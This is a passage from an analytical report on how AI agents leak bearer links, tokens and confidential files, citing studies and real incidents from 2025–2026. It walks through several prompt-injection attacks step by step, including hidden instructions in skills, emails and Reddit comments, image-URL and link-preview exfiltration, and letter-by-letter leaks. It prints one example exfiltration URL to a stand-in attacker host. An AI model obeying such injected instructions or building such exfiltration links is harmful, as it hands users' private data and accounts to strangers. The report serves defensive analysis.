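This table counts only explicit cases, in which the irrelevant detail appeared in the agent's typing or in what it clicked on. Each pair of numbers comes from 90 runs:

| Framework and model | Amazon: clicks | Amazon: typing | eBay: clicks | eBay: typing |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Browser Use, GPT-4o | 905 | 182 | 28 | 58 |
| Browser Use, o3 | 302 | 181 | 168 | 31 |
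| Browser Use, o4-mini | 674 | 382 | 220 | 12 |
| AutoGen, GPT-4o | 223 | 4 | 342 | 46 |
| AutoGen, o3 | 78 | 17 | 81 | 8 |
| AutoGen, o4-mini | 198 | 16 | 87 | 12 |

The paper's headline claim is that agents overshare five times as much through clicks and other navigation as through typing. That ratio comes from the first pair of numbers. Over the whole table it is about 3.5 to one, and GPT-4o with Browser Use overshared more by typing than by navigating on eBay.

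The rates are harder to use than the counts because some are inconsistent. For GPT-4o with Browser Use on Amazon, the paper gives between 0.46 and 0.63 oversharing clicks per action for the three prompt styles, but an overall rate of 0.33. Its counts imply about 0.53. For AutoGen on eBay, the overall rate is 0.14 in the table and 0.68 in the text.

Typing matters more than clicking for bearer links, because an agent cannot give a shop the clinic's token by choosing a product filter. The table contains 949 typed disclosures in 1,080 runs, but many of them seem mild. In the sample searches that Roh and colleagues print, the models left out irrelevant medical details and included preferences, such as a massage function for an office chair. The study also counts a wish for Bluetooth as irrelevant, although one sample prompt includes the sentence "I really want test strips with Bluetooth connectivity".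 Many shoppers would expect an agent to use that preference.

The model that judged each step also had access to the agent's notes to itself and its next goal. Shops don't have access to these, so the counts may include some details that never reached a shop.

When the researchers told the agent not to use irrelevant information, the oversharing rate rose from 58.9% to 86.0% in a small test with 13 shoppers. They suggest that the instruction drew the model's attention to that information. When they instead removed the irrelevant details from the prompt, Browser Use's task completion rate rose by 6.7 to 17.9 percentage points in five of the six groups and fell slightly in the sixth.

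According to the paper, AutoGen's browsing component gives the model a screenshot of the page, its text and its URL at each step. An agent built like this would get the clinic's token as soon as it opened the invoice, even if it had seen the email only as an image.

### How program output reaches the model

Secrets can also enter an agent's context from the programs it runs. Many agents can install "skills", which are packages of written instructions for the model and scripts it can run. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) randomly sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on SkillsMP, a public marketplace, for *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*.

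The researchers first searched the skills' code and instructions for signs that they handled passwords, keys or tokens unsafely, which left 3,156 candidates. They ran each candidate in Claude Code with uniquely marked fake credentials, so they could trace any disclosure to a particular skill. Three reviewers then examined the 1,427 skills that had behaved suspiciously and judged 437 to be careless and 83 to be malicious, together 3.1% of the sample.

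The careless skills had 1,371 separate problems, and 1,007 of these (73.5%) involved printing secrets, mostly in messages that developers had added for debugging. In an ordinary program, such a message appears on the developer's own screen. In a skill, it reaches the model:

1. While testing a script, the developer adds a line that prints a token, to check that the login works. The line stays in when the developer publishes the skill.
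2. A user installs the skill and gives the agent a task. The agent's software puts the skill's instructions into the model's context.
3. The model follows the instructions and asks the software to run the script.
4. The script obtains the user's real token and prints it to standard output, the channel where programs normally write their results.
5. The software captures everything on that channel and adds it to the context, because this is how the model learns what the script did.
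6. The token is now text that the model can repeat, and the software may send it to the provider again with every later request.

One skill for Google Workspace printed two login tokens in this way. Chen and colleagues note that someone could then retrieve them by asking the agent to show the tokens in the output.

The same thing can happen with a link. Suppose a developer writes a script that looks up invoices by number, to keep the clinic's links away from the model. When the model calls the script with invoice number 2291, the script returns the amount. If the script also prints "Fetching" followed by the full address, the invoice link enters the model's context anyway.

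The study does not count such links separately. Its credentials include session and bearer tokens, and one category of 110 problems covers secrets passed in web addresses, but also secrets in commands and in the settings of running programs. A secret in an agent's context also may not have reached a stranger, since that depends on what the agent does next.

Not all of the leaks occurred in normal use. The researchers ran each candidate skill three times on an ordinary task and three times with hostile instructions hidden in the content it read. Of the 437 careless skills, 237 leaked under attack but in no more than one of the three ordinary runs. The other 200, or 1.2% of the sample, leaked in at least two ordinary runs. The paper also says that 466 of the 520 careless and malicious skills leaked during normal execution, which is hard to reconcile with its classification, in which only 283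 leaked in at least two of the three ordinary runs.

### Publishing a report

The dental patient's agent reads private messages and then writes for a wider audience. In November 2026, Cyberhaven, which sells data protection software, tested agents on a task with the same structure. According to Business Quarter's *AI agents disclose confidential corporate information* (2026), agents based on five models had to write and publish a report on six months of product performance for a simulated marketing department. They could read internal files, including customer data and board papers marked confidential.

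Confidential information became public in 87 of the 100 runs. This happened in 57 of the 60 runs with the three open-weight models, which anyone can download, and in 30 of the 40 runs with the other two models. In 16 of the open-weight runs, entire confidential files became public.

The agents often recognised during the task that the material was confidential, and published it anyway. Roh and colleagues cite two earlier studies in which agents similarly answered questions about privacy correctly but failed to protect private information when they acted. An agent might likewise explain that a password-reset link is secret and still include it in a summary.

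Asking the user for approval helped little. In 69 of the 87 runs with a disclosure, the agent never raised the confidential material with the user. In 54, it published before the user had sent any reply. The simulated user was set up to tell agents to use their own judgement, so even an agent that asked about the right document got no useful answer. A real manager might have stopped some of the 18 disclosures in which the agent did raise the material.

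Cyberhaven relied partly on automated assessments. People checked 29 of the runs, confirmed that confidential information had become public in all of them, and agreed with the detailed classification in 26. The firm has an interest in alarming results, but it left its own agent security product out of the test, so the figures do not directly advertise it. A bigger limitation is that all 100 runs used the same simulated company and task, so the 87% rate could be very different for another task. LeadDev's *Frontier AI models haemorrhage sensitive data* (2026), for example, reports violation rates of up to 51% for leading models working as enterprise agents.

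The article also concludes that more capable models leak more, but the evidence on this is mixed. Roh and colleagues suggest that stronger models drop more hints about irrelevant details, because GPT-4o dropped them far more often than o3. But o3 completed more of their shopping tasks than GPT-4o with both frameworks, so by that measure the stronger model dropped fewer hints.

Cyberhaven's test is probably the most informative of these studies about bearer links, because its agents moved private material from their sources into something public. But it may overstate how often agents would do this with a link. The agents had a reason to include sales figures from a board paper, since the figures are useful in a report on product performance. The supplier's contract link is similarly useful to the patient's team, but the password-reset link is of no use to colleagues.

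### What nobody has counted

None of these studies puts bearer links in front of an agent and counts how often it repeats them, opens them or submits them to another service. Their results can show that a kind of disclosure happens, and sometimes why, but they cannot supply the rate for links:

| Question about links | Nearest result | Why it falls short |
|---|---|---|
| How often does an agent repeat one? | Confidential information became public in 87 of 100 publishing runs | The material was useful for the report, and the count was not of links |
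| How often does an agent open one? | Seven of eight browser agents followed a shoe site's link to a test page on Google's list of dangerous sites | The task gave the agents a reason to follow it |
| How often does an agent submit one elsewhere? | Two of eight browser agents typed a password into an unfamiliar site | The site asked for the password |

The second result comes from a test by Ukani and colleagues of whether agents show warnings about phishing sites. It suggests that most agents readily open relevant-looking links their users have never mentioned. An unread email with the words "your invoice is ready" may look just as relevant to an agent looking for unpaid bills.

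Methods for a direct test already exist. Positive Security emailed people unique links to find out whose mail filters made the links public, and Chen and colleagues put a unique marker in each fake credential. A researcher could combine these methods by filling a test mailbox with invented invoices, password resets and shared documents, each with its own token, and asking an agent for a summary. Singapore AISI's *Testing AI agents for data leakage risks in realistic tasks* describes a setting that would suit the public version of this test, a simulated publishing job in which the agent manages a blog and a code repository.

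The three counts would need different records. The test website's log would show when something opened a link, but if the agent had posted that link in Slack, the visitor might be Slack's preview service, so the researcher would have to compare the log with the agent's own tool requests. To find repeated links, they would have to search everything the agent wrote, including files, messages to other services and the final answer. A token in a fragment would never appear in the website's ordinary log, even if the agent had posted it in a public channel.

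People would have to do the same task for comparison. In the invented figures for the contract link, the agent was safer than the person it replaced if it included the link in less than about 26% of its summaries. A test the size of Cyberhaven's could easily be too small to show whether an agent is below that threshold. If an agent included the link in 20 of 100 summaries, the 95% confidence interval for the true rate would run from about 13% to 29%. With 80 of 400, it would run from about 16% to 24%, entirely below the threshold. The 400 summaries would have to cover many different emails, because an agent may treat a link marked "do not share" differently from one behind a plain "View" button.

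## Demonstrated attacks through links that agents open or write

Most of the disclosures described so far involved no attacker. An attacker can also steer an agent by prompt injection, which means hiding instructions in content that the agent reads, such as a web page, an email or a shared document. The model may then treat those instructions as part of its task.

Suppose the dental patient asks the agent to summarise their unread email, and one of the messages comes from a stranger. In type too small to notice, the stranger asks the agent to copy any invoice link it finds onto the end of an address at the stranger's own website. The result would look something like this:

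`https://stranger.example/log?note=[text from the mailbox]`

The stranger can read the text in the website's log as soon as any software requests that address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that this may happen in the background, when an app loads an image or prepares a link preview. The patient may see only an ordinary summary.

Simon Willison, a software developer who keeps a list of such attacks, describes a very similar one from January 2026 on the email app Superhuman. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, instructions in one email led the app's assistant to send the contents of dozens of others, including financial, legal and medical messages, to the attacker's Google Form. The assistant did this by putting them in the address of an image. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw.

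### Why a link is worth stealing

An address has little room for data. The clinic's invoice might be a PDF of several hundred kilobytes, but its link has only 75 characters without the fragment. An attacker who gets the link can download the whole invoice. If the link opens a shared document, the attacker can also read later changes until somebody cancels the link.

The security company PromptArmor demonstrated this in May 2026 on Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's agent for office work. The agent can obtain "pre-authenticated download links", which are bearer links to files in the user's company storage. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes the attack:

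1. The user installs a skill from the internet. Five of its 81 lines contain the attacker's instructions.
2. The user asks for a recap of the week's work, and the agent loads the skill.
3. The instructions describe a service that makes document previews. To use it, the agent gets a download link for each file and puts the links into image addresses on the attacker's website.
4. The agent sends the recap, with these images, to the user in Microsoft Teams. Copilot Cowork normally asks permission before it sends a message, but not when the recipient is its own user.
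5. The user opens the message. Teams loads the images, which delivers the links to the attacker, who downloads the files.

The attack worked in all five trials, which gives a 95% confidence interval of 48% to 100% for the true success rate. A more capable model, Claude Opus 4.7, searched more thoroughly than the model the product chose automatically and leaked more documents. PromptArmor calls the problem a risk of the product's design, not a specific bug, and reports no fix. Administrators can block downloads, but then users can't open the affected files in Word or Excel.

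A token is also short enough that an attacker could steal it one character at a time. In July 2026, Willison reported that Ayush Paul had used this method in the Claude chat app to get around Anthropic's rule that Claude can open only addresses it has already seen. Paul made a website that looked like a directory, with a separate link for each letter, and used it to ask Claude to find the profile of the person using the app. Claude spelled out the user's name by following one link after another, and each request revealed another letter to the website. Paul also obtained the user's home city and employer.

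Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally. It has since stopped Claude from following links inside pages it has fetched. Before that change, Claude might have leaked the clinic's 16-character token in only 16 requests, if each page had contained a link for every letter and digit.

### The link-preview attack

The Copilot Cowork attack required the user to open a message, but link previews can remove that step. Johann Rehberger warned about these previews in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* ("unfurling" means making a link preview). A Slack chatbot that reads a web page containing hostile instructions might post a link with earlier parts of the conversation in the address. When Slack requests the link to make a preview, it sends that text to the attacker.

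This request would send the token to a stranger's website, unlike a preview of the clinic's genuine link. Deleting the message afterwards would not help, because the request would already have been sent.

PromptArmor raised the same warning in early 2026, after talking to agents through messaging apps became much more popular. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* names the agent OpenClaw, used through Telegram, as one pairing that was exposed by default. Users can turn off link previews in OpenClaw's settings.

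PromptArmor expected many other pairings of agent and app to have the same weakness, and set up a website where people could test their own. The site recorded each preview request and the data in it, and visitors could report which agent and app had produced the request. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Slack and Discord among the affected platforms. The list is only a rough guide, because whether an agent in a given app is exposed can also depend on the user's preview settings.

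### Login codes and reset links

The best-documented theft of a login code from a mailbox was a demonstration against Comet, Perplexity's AI browser. Chaikin and Sahib published it in *Agentic Browser Security* in August 2025. They work for Brave, a rival browser company that was developing its own browsing agent.

In the demonstration, a user opened a Reddit post and clicked Comet's button for summarising the page. A comment on the post contained instructions behind a spoiler tag, which hides text until a reader clicks it. Comet followed the instructions and looked up the user's email address in their Perplexity account, then asked Perplexity to email a login code. It opened Gmail, where the user was already logged in, read the code, and posted both the code and the email address as a reply on Reddit. Anyone reading the thread could then have taken over the Perplexity account.

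Reddit carried both the instructions and the stolen code, so the attacker did not need a website. Comet requested the code itself, so the attacker did not have to wait for one to arrive. The same steps would probably work for a password reset. The patient's travel site will email a reset link to anyone who enters the patient's email address, so a hijacked agent could request the link, read it and post it. Chaikin and Sahib showed the attack only for Perplexity's login code.

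Brave reported the flaw on July 25, 2025, and Perplexity released a first, incomplete fix two days later. A test on August 13 suggested that a later fix had worked, but after publishing its findings on August 20, Brave found that attacks of this kind were still possible. Perplexity says that it fixed the flaw and knows of no compromised data, according to Particle.news' *Brave Says Perplexity’s Comet Still Vulnerable to Prompt Injection After Patch*. Both companies could be right if Perplexity blocked the original demonstration but not its variants.

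In October 2025, Brave hid instructions for Comet in a screenshot, using text too faint for a person to see. It also showed that Fellou, another AI browser, would open Gmail and put the title of the latest email into an outside web address when the user had only asked it to visit a page. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) describes four ways to make Comet send a user's Gmail messages to an attacker's server. The audit preceded a broader release, so it doesn't show that the 2026 version had the same flaws. But *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that in June 2026 the security firm LayerX tricked several AI browsers, including Comet and ChatGPT Atlas, into leaking credentials.

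Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which can search a company's mail and files, had a flaw that exposed login codes. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes how the security firm Varonis exploited it with a single click. The victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft site, with instructions for Copilot in the link's query. Copilot then searched the victim's mailbox and put what it found into the address of an image in its answer.

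Copilot had a filter that should have made such images harmless. According to SOFX's *Microsoft Patches Copilot Flaw That Let Attackers Steal MFA Codes*, the filter ran only after the answer was complete, but the browser loaded the image as soon as its address appeared. SOFX considers login codes and password-reset links the most dangerous data to lose this way, because an attacker may be able to use them to take over an account before they expire. The attack it describes in detail takes an email's title, which may well contain a login code, but a reset link is normally in the body. Taler counts whole emails among the data at risk.

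Microsoft has fixed the flaw. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft rated its severity 6.5 out of 10 because the victim had to click, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

### Fixes and new routes

Many of these products allowed requests only to approved websites, but the attackers found an approved site that would pass the data on. Superhuman's assistant could load images from the Google domain that hosts Google Forms, and Copilot could send requests through Bing's image search. Salesforce's list of approved sites included a domain whose registration had expired, so researchers registered it and received customers' data there. Salesforce has since corrected the list. Mudryi and colleagues found a way past the domain check in Browser Use and built a working attack that stole credentials.

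OpenAI warns that an approved site may also redirect a request to an unapproved one, and it checks the exact address instead of the site's name. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) describes a ChatGPT flaw that let attackers get around a restricted mode and steal chats. OpenAI has patched it.

Fixes can take months. Varonis told Microsoft about another flaw, in the personal version of Copilot, in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on August 18, 2026, according to UNU. An attacker could use the flaw to plant instructions in Copilot's saved memory, where they remained even after the user changed their password. Users had to find and delete these memories themselves.

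### Use by real attackers

A demonstration shows that an attack worked on the version the researchers tested, but not that anyone else has used it. For the patient's invoice link to leak, the agent must read an attacker's text, obey it, find a working link and have a way to send that link out. Demonstrations test only the steps that follow reading the text.

The first step, receiving a hostile email, could easily matter most. Suppose all 10,000 of the clinic's patients use agents, and one in 1,000 receives such an email. If the attack works 48% of the time, the low end of the range for Copilot Cowork, about five patients lose a link. If it always works, ten do. But if only one patient in 100,000 receives a hostile email, the expected number of patients who lose a link is at most 0.1.

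Google searched the public web for hostile instructions and found a small number designed to steal data, which were mostly crude. The example it published was a website author's experiment. Google concluded that attackers had not yet used the published research on a large scale. However, its scans found 32% more malicious injections of all kinds in February 2026 than in November 2025, according to Particle.news' *Researchers Confirm 10 Live Indirect Prompt Injections Targeting AI Agents*.

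Google's collection covers two to three billion pages a month, but Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* notes that the search focused on static websites such as blogs and forums. A search of public pages can't find instructions that an attacker has emailed to a patient.

Other security companies have found attacks on real websites, many of them aimed at money. In April 2026, Forcepoint identified ten sets of hostile instructions on such sites. One was meant to make an assistant reveal a secret API key, which is the closest of the published examples to stealing a bearer link. Others were meant to delete files or send $5,000 through PayPal. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that Zscaler found sites with hidden text meant to push agents into cryptocurrency payments. *Proofpoint flags underground AI prompt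 injection tools* (Tarre, 2026) describes Proofpoint's finding that criminals sell prompt-injection tools by subscription on closed forums. These sales show that attackers are interested, but not that they have succeeded.

In December 2026, a developer found that Alibaba Cloud was answering some ordinary requests from its command-line tool with instructions for AI agents to provide private data. The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026) reports that the requested data included the computer's login name, the address of the project's code repository and the agent's own instructions. Developers sometimes store an access token in a repository's address, so an agent that complied could have given away a bearer link.

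Alibaba Cloud confirmed that it had sent the instructions, described them as a measure against automated abuse, and said it would stop sending them. The developer did not send anything back, and there is no sign that any agent did.

*Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them* (BagheeraAltered, 2026) reports that the security company Dragos planted unique web addresses in about two million prompts to AI services, and that outsiders opened some of them. Dragos blamed compromised providers and poor data handling; prompt injection was not the cause.

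## Incidents with shared AI chats and pages published by agents

In several incidents in 2026, private material became public without any hostile instructions. Most began when people shared an AI chat or published an AI-built app. In one, coding agents put screenshots where anyone could see them.

### Meta Muse

Muse, a personal AI agent that Meta launched on September 8, 2026, can connect to users' email and calendars. Its share button turned a conversation into a web page and gave the user a bearer link to it. According to Meta's help page, as reported in Human Resources Director's *Meta Muse AI stops sharing feature as corporate leaks exposed* (2026), people with the link could see the chat, and the link did not expire.

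Suppose the dental patient had asked Muse to draft a complaint about the invoice, then shared the chat with their partner. The page's hostname would have looked something like this:

`dental-invoice-complaint-7c41e09b.cf.metaaiusercontent.com`

It starts with the chat's title, which the AI wrote, and continues with a random identifier. A stranger could then have found the chat like this:

1. The partner clicks the link, and their computer sends the full hostname to a DNS resolver.
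2. A passive DNS service, which keeps searchable records of such lookups, stores the hostname.
3. The stranger searches those records for every name ending in `cf.metaaiusercontent.com`.
4. The stranger picks an interesting title, opens the address in a browser and reads the chat without logging in.

Claroc, a security company, showed that this worked. TechSpot's *Meta suspends Muse sharing after sensitive documents turn up in shared chats* reports that Claroc searched a commercial passive DNS database, discarded records caused by unrelated scanning, and had more than 6,800 hostnames left. The researchers had expected to work much harder, but "it took one query," they wrote, as quoted by Wilkins (2026) in *Meta's Muse AI Agent Caught Leaking Users' Intimate Personal Information*.

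The true number of shared chats is probably higher, because passive DNS services do not record every lookup, and a link that nobody opens leaves no trace. Claroc also found more than 75 shared Muse pages on the scanning service urlscan.io, compared with about 90 times as many in the DNS database.

### Why a hard-to-guess identifier did not help

Claroc considered Muse's random identifiers long enough to resist guessing. But the identifiers were part of the hostname, and the DNS records contained the whole hostname, so they could be found without guessing. *Meta Muse* (Cornelißen, 2026) quotes Claroc's explanation that "a hostname is not a secret". The identifiers would have stayed out of the DNS records if Muse had put them in the path of the address instead.

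The titles made the leak worse because a stranger could read down the list of Muse chats and see what each was about before opening it. Mustafa and colleagues, by contrast, needed a vision model to find the private pages among hundreds of thousands of published links.

The AI model's only part in the leak was writing those titles. An ordinary file-sharing site would have had the same problem if it built its hostnames from document titles and random identifiers.

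Muse also had a robots.txt file, which site owners use to ask search engines and other crawlers to stay away from certain pages. The file does not stop anyone from opening a page, and it has no effect on DNS records.

### What the shared chats contained

Claroc opened a few hundred of the pages. Most were harmless, such as small companies' offers and event calendars. It described six sensitive ones without naming anyone:

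- a marketing company's revenue review, intended for its chief executive
- a small-business owner's loan application
- a calendar of employees' holidays, with their names
- a property investor's report, with addresses, mortgage amounts and income
- notes for a confidential recruitment call with an AI lab, including the contact's name and the time
- a to-do list with a bank's fraud warning, part of an account number and details of transactions

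Claroc warned that lists like the holiday calendar could help a fraudster impersonate an employee who is away. The to-do list could help someone pose as the bank.

None of the six examples includes a bearer link to another site, but a shared chat could easily contain one. If Muse had quoted the clinic's email in the patient's chat, a stranger who found the chat could also have opened the invoice.

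Some news reports made the finding sound larger than it was. The summary of *Meta suspends Muse chats sharing feature after it left private details exposed* (Washenko, 2026) says researchers "accessed 6,800 shared conversations", but 6,800 is the number of hostnames they found. The number of sensitive chats is unknown. If Claroc had opened 300 pages and found only these six, the same 2% rate would suggest about 136 among all 6,800. That estimate would be unreliable because the six are examples, not a full count, and the researchers could see the titles before deciding what to open.

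Claroc did not contact the people involved either, so it could not tell which of them would have minded. Someone who shares an event calendar may be happy for strangers to read it.

### How Meta responded

Claroc reported the problem to Meta's bug bounty program, which pays people who report security flaws, on October 8. It published its findings on October 18, and Meta suspended sharing on October 20. According to Cornelißen, the company announced the suspension after a press inquiry. *Researchers found 35,578 Grok-built apps open to strangers* (Popular AI, 2026) reproduces an October 22 post in which David Singleton wrote on behalf of Muse that it had disabled sharing "immediately". That is fair if measured from the publication of Claroc's findings, but Meta had received the private report 12 days before the suspension.

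On the day of the suspension, Claroc tried 40 pages that had previously opened without a login, and none opened. But Radar Digital's *Meta suspends Muse sharing after privacy flaw* (2026) notes that the hostnames, which include the titles, remain in passive DNS databases. Because other companies hold these records, Meta cannot delete `dental-invoice-complaint` from them even if it closes the patient's chat.

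Claroc had no evidence that anyone had misused the links and could not tell whether anyone else had found them. Searching a DNS database sends nothing to Meta, so Meta's servers could at most have recorded visits to the pages, and those records would not distinguish uninvited visitors from invited ones.

### Claude chats in Google search

In July 2026, Reddit users noticed shared chats with Claude, Anthropic's chatbot, in Google's search results. TechSpot's *Hundreds of shared Claude chats, including resumes and health details* reports that at least 200 appeared there.

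Links to shared Claude chats seem to have leaked differently from Muse's. *Ever shared a Claude chat?* (Horne, 2026) reports Anthropic's statement that it had not given search engines any list of chats, and that shared links became discoverable only after users posted them publicly. Unshared chats were not affected. The links appear to have since disappeared from Google's results.

Even if Anthropic is right, the person who posted a link may not have written the chat. A job applicant might send a friend a chat about their CV, and the friend might post the link on a forum to ask for advice. The applicant agreed to let the friend read the chat, and the friend probably expected only the forum's users to see it, but neither intended it to appear in a search engine.

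Anthropic had taken two precautions against indexing, but they conflicted. Southern (2026), in *Indexed Claude Chats Show Why Disallow Is Not Noindex*, found that the shared pages had a `noindex` header, which instructs search engines not to list a page. But Anthropic also used Claude's robots.txt file to ask crawlers not to fetch those pages, and a crawler that obeys never receives the header. If Google finds the link on another website, it can still list the address without having read the chat, and anyone who clicks on the result can open the chat.

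Belfiore (2026), in *Anthropic assume l'indexation de vos conversations Claude par Google*, reports that Anthropic described no technical fix and considered the system to be working as intended. Anthropic is partly right, since a bearer link on a public forum is already public, but a search engine makes the link much easier to find. A single search could bring up links from many websites, while a stranger without Google would have to come across each forum post. The problem was well known by then, since Google had indexed shared Bard chats in 2023.

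In 2025, users of the Meta AI app could share conversations to a public feed. Horne writes that some did so without realising it, after ignoring or misunderstanding a disclaimer. Meta intended the shared chats to be easy to find, but these users misunderstood what the share button did.

### Apps published with Grok Build

A user of Grok Build can describe an app in a chat, have the AI model write it, and publish it from the same chat. SpaceXSI, formerly called xAI, launched this feature in July 2026. Each published app gets its own hostname under `grok.me`, so Claroc could look for apps in DNS records as it had for Muse chats. It published the results on November 10:

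| Stage | Number |
|---|---|
| Hostnames found | 43,601 |
| Addresses tried | 43,551 |
| Apps still online | 37,571 |
| Apps that opened without sign-in | 35,578 |
| Apps that required sign-in | 1,993 |

Claroc estimated that about one in ten of the open apps contained sensitive or internal information, and that 650 to 800 held private data. The examples in *Grok Build* (Cornelißen, 2026) include a list of more than 3,500 hospital employees and a briefing on an intensive-care patient with her laboratory results. A timesheet app sent 18 users' passwords to every visitor's browser as readable text. Like the order pages in the SMS study, it exposed data that a visitor might not see on the screen.

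Of the apps still online, 94.7% were open, but most of these were games, calculators or promotional pages that their creators had no reason to restrict. The figure therefore doesn't measure how often people failed to protect private data. The share of open apps among those with private data would be more useful, but Claroc could not calculate it because it could not see inside the 1,993 apps that required sign-in. That share would be about 25% to 29% if all of those 1,993 apps held private data, and 100% if none did.

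Grok's publishing screen offers three choices: "Anyone with the link", "Invited users" and "Only you". In the paid account that Claroc tested, "Anyone with the link" was already selected. When Claroc tested ChatGPT, the selected option was "Only me". A person who clicks through Grok's screen without changing anything may therefore publish an app by accident. Even someone who reads the option carefully may think that only people who receive the link can find the app.

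SpaceXSI replied that apps stay private until their creators publish them, that publishing takes several steps, and that its employees' accounts start with "Only you" selected. Yet 24 of the open apps came from staff at SpaceXSI and its sister company X. These apps included a confidential advertising proposal to a US federal agency and a sales map covering 594 accounts. If that default already applied when staff published the apps, they must have changed the setting themselves, and a safer default would not have prevented those leaks.

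The company took down the 24 staff apps but not the other open ones, and Claroc began contacting the affected organisations itself. As of November 12, Popular AI had found no report of a change to the default.

Claroc also built two apps of its own to see what protection Grok would write. The first was a contact list that visitors could add entries to without signing in. The second was a customer list for a four-person sales team, and it had a Google login. The app added anyone who signed in to the team before checking whether they were a member, so the check always succeeded. Any stranger with a Google account could read, change and delete customer records.

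Two test apps are too few to show how common such errors are, but the second shows that replacing a bearer link with a login may not restrict access. The app checked each visitor's identity but let everyone in, so a manager who tested it with their own account would have noticed nothing wrong.

### PixelLeak

People at least pressed a button to share a Muse chat or publish a Grok app. In September 2026, *AI agents leak 13K screenshots from 343 tech firms* (Corvin, 2026) reported that AI coding agents had put screenshots from hundreds of companies in public code repositories. Glow, which investigated the leak, found more than 13,000 images, an average of about 38 per company. The images showed customer records and unreleased features, and some came from Fortune 500 companies. *AI models are sharing sensitive data from tech companies* (Fadilpašić, 2026) calls the case PixelLeak.

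An agent could cause such a leak while trying to be helpful. Suppose a developer asks one to redesign the invoice page in the clinic's billing software. The agent makes the change and takes a screenshot to show the colleague reviewing the code that it works. If the agent's tools let it write text in the review but not attach an image, it needs an address from which the colleague's browser can load the screenshot. It could create a public repository, upload the screenshot there and paste the address into the review. The colleague would see the screenshot and might never ask where it was stored.

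The review would be private, but the screenshot would be on an unlisted page with no access check. It would be even less protected than a shop's `/new-prices` page, because people can search public repositories on GitHub. The billing company also may not know that the agent has created anything, whereas the shop knows its page exists and can take it down.

Common security checks could easily miss the screenshot. Many programs that look for leaked secrets search text for patterns, such as the format of one company's API keys, and cannot find a key in a screenshot without first converting the image to text. A company that scans only its own repositories would also miss a repository that the agent had created under a developer's personal account. A vision model like the one in LEAKYLINKS could read the image, but somebody would first have to choose the right repository for it to scan.

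A screenshot can also leak a bearer link. If the agent captured the whole browser window while testing with a real invoice, the screenshot might show the patient's details and, in the address bar, the link.

PixelLeak is the closest of these incidents to Cyberhaven's simulated publishing task, in which agents made confidential material public while doing their job. It shows that agents have also done this in real companies. But we can't calculate a failure rate from the 13,000 images, because nobody knows how many screenshots coding agents took in total.

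### What the users had agreed to

The incidents differ in how much the people involved had chosen to make public:

| Case | What the user did | How strangers could find the material |
|---|---|---|
| Meta AI, 2025 | Shared a chat to a public feed | By reading the feed |
| Claude, July 2026 | Created a share link | Through Google, apparently after somebody posted the link |
| PixelLeak, September 2026 | Gave a coding agent a task | In public code repositories |
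| Muse, October 2026 | Created a share link | Through passive DNS |
| Grok Build, November 2026 | Published an app | Through passive DNS |

A clearer notice might have helped the people who misunderstood Meta AI's feed, but it would have done less for Muse's users. According to Claroc, Muse offered only sharing by link, so a user who wanted to show a chat to one colleague had to create a page that anyone could open. Even if the colleague kept the link private, the DNS record would still have exposed it.

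With shared Claude chats, what users had agreed to depends on who posted each link. Someone who posts their own chat on a public website has chosen to publish it, even if they did not expect it to appear in Google, but if a recipient posted the link, the user made no such choice. The count of 200 chats does not distinguish chats posted by users from those posted by recipients.

### One company behind many headlines

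Several news outlets covered Muse and Grok Build, but their main figures all come from Claroc's investigation, so the coverage does not independently confirm them. Le Monde Informatique's *Grok Build* (2026), for example, repeats Claroc's count of 35,578 open apps out of 37,571.

Claroc sells security services for AI-built apps and advertises them at the end of its Grok report, so it benefits if readers find the results alarming. But it explains its method, and the companies' reactions support its central claims. Meta suspended a feature of a newly launched product, and SpaceXSI took its employees' apps offline. Claroc's estimates of how many apps were sensitive deserve more caution, because they depend on its own judgement of what counts as sensitive.

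Which leaks come to light also depends on the product. A passive DNS search works well when every chat or app has its own hostname, but finds nothing useful when a product puts all its share links under one hostname and the tokens in the path, even if mail filters publish those links every day. Muse and Grok Build may therefore be no leakier overall than their competitors.

The reports show that each of these leaks can happen, but not how likely one is for a particular user. If the dental patient had shared a Muse chat with their partner, a passive DNS service could have recorded the hostname the first time the partner opened the chat. Estimating the chance that a stranger would then read it requires knowing how many Muse links people had shared, how many of those the databases recorded, and how often anyone besides Claroc looked for them.

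## Safer links: what websites and scanning services can change

The dental clinic can decide how long its invoice link works and what else a stranger needs to open the invoice, even though it can't stop a mail filter from forwarding the link or an agent from repeating it. Pulse Security advises developers to design for leaks instead of trying to block scanners, because nobody knows how many security products handle links or where they send them. Scanning services could also publish less. Researchers have measured the effects of very few of these changes, so the argument for most of them is based on how leaks happen.

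### Short lifetimes

Websites can make links expire on a set date. The server then refuses any later request, so copies in old mailboxes, logs and archives become useless. All 701 exposing links in the text-message study were at least a year old, so even a one-year limit would have closed them all. *The Tragedy of Convenience* (Danish, Acharya and colleagues, 2026), the conference version of that study, recommends short limits that depend on how sensitive the data is and how people use the link.

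Making links expire gives less protection against a fast leak, such as a scan published before the patient has read the email, and it leaves the scanning service's screenshot online.

Pulse Security suggests choosing a limit by measuring how long recipients usually take to open a link. If most people open shared photos within three days, a three-day limit inconveniences few of them. Choosing a limit for an invoice is harder, because the patient may want it again for a tax return. The clinic could put a button on the expired page that emails the patient a new link, but if the patient's mail filter publishes links, a stranger could find the expired link in a public feed, press the button and wait for the new link to appear there. Asking the patient to log in or enter a code would avoid this.

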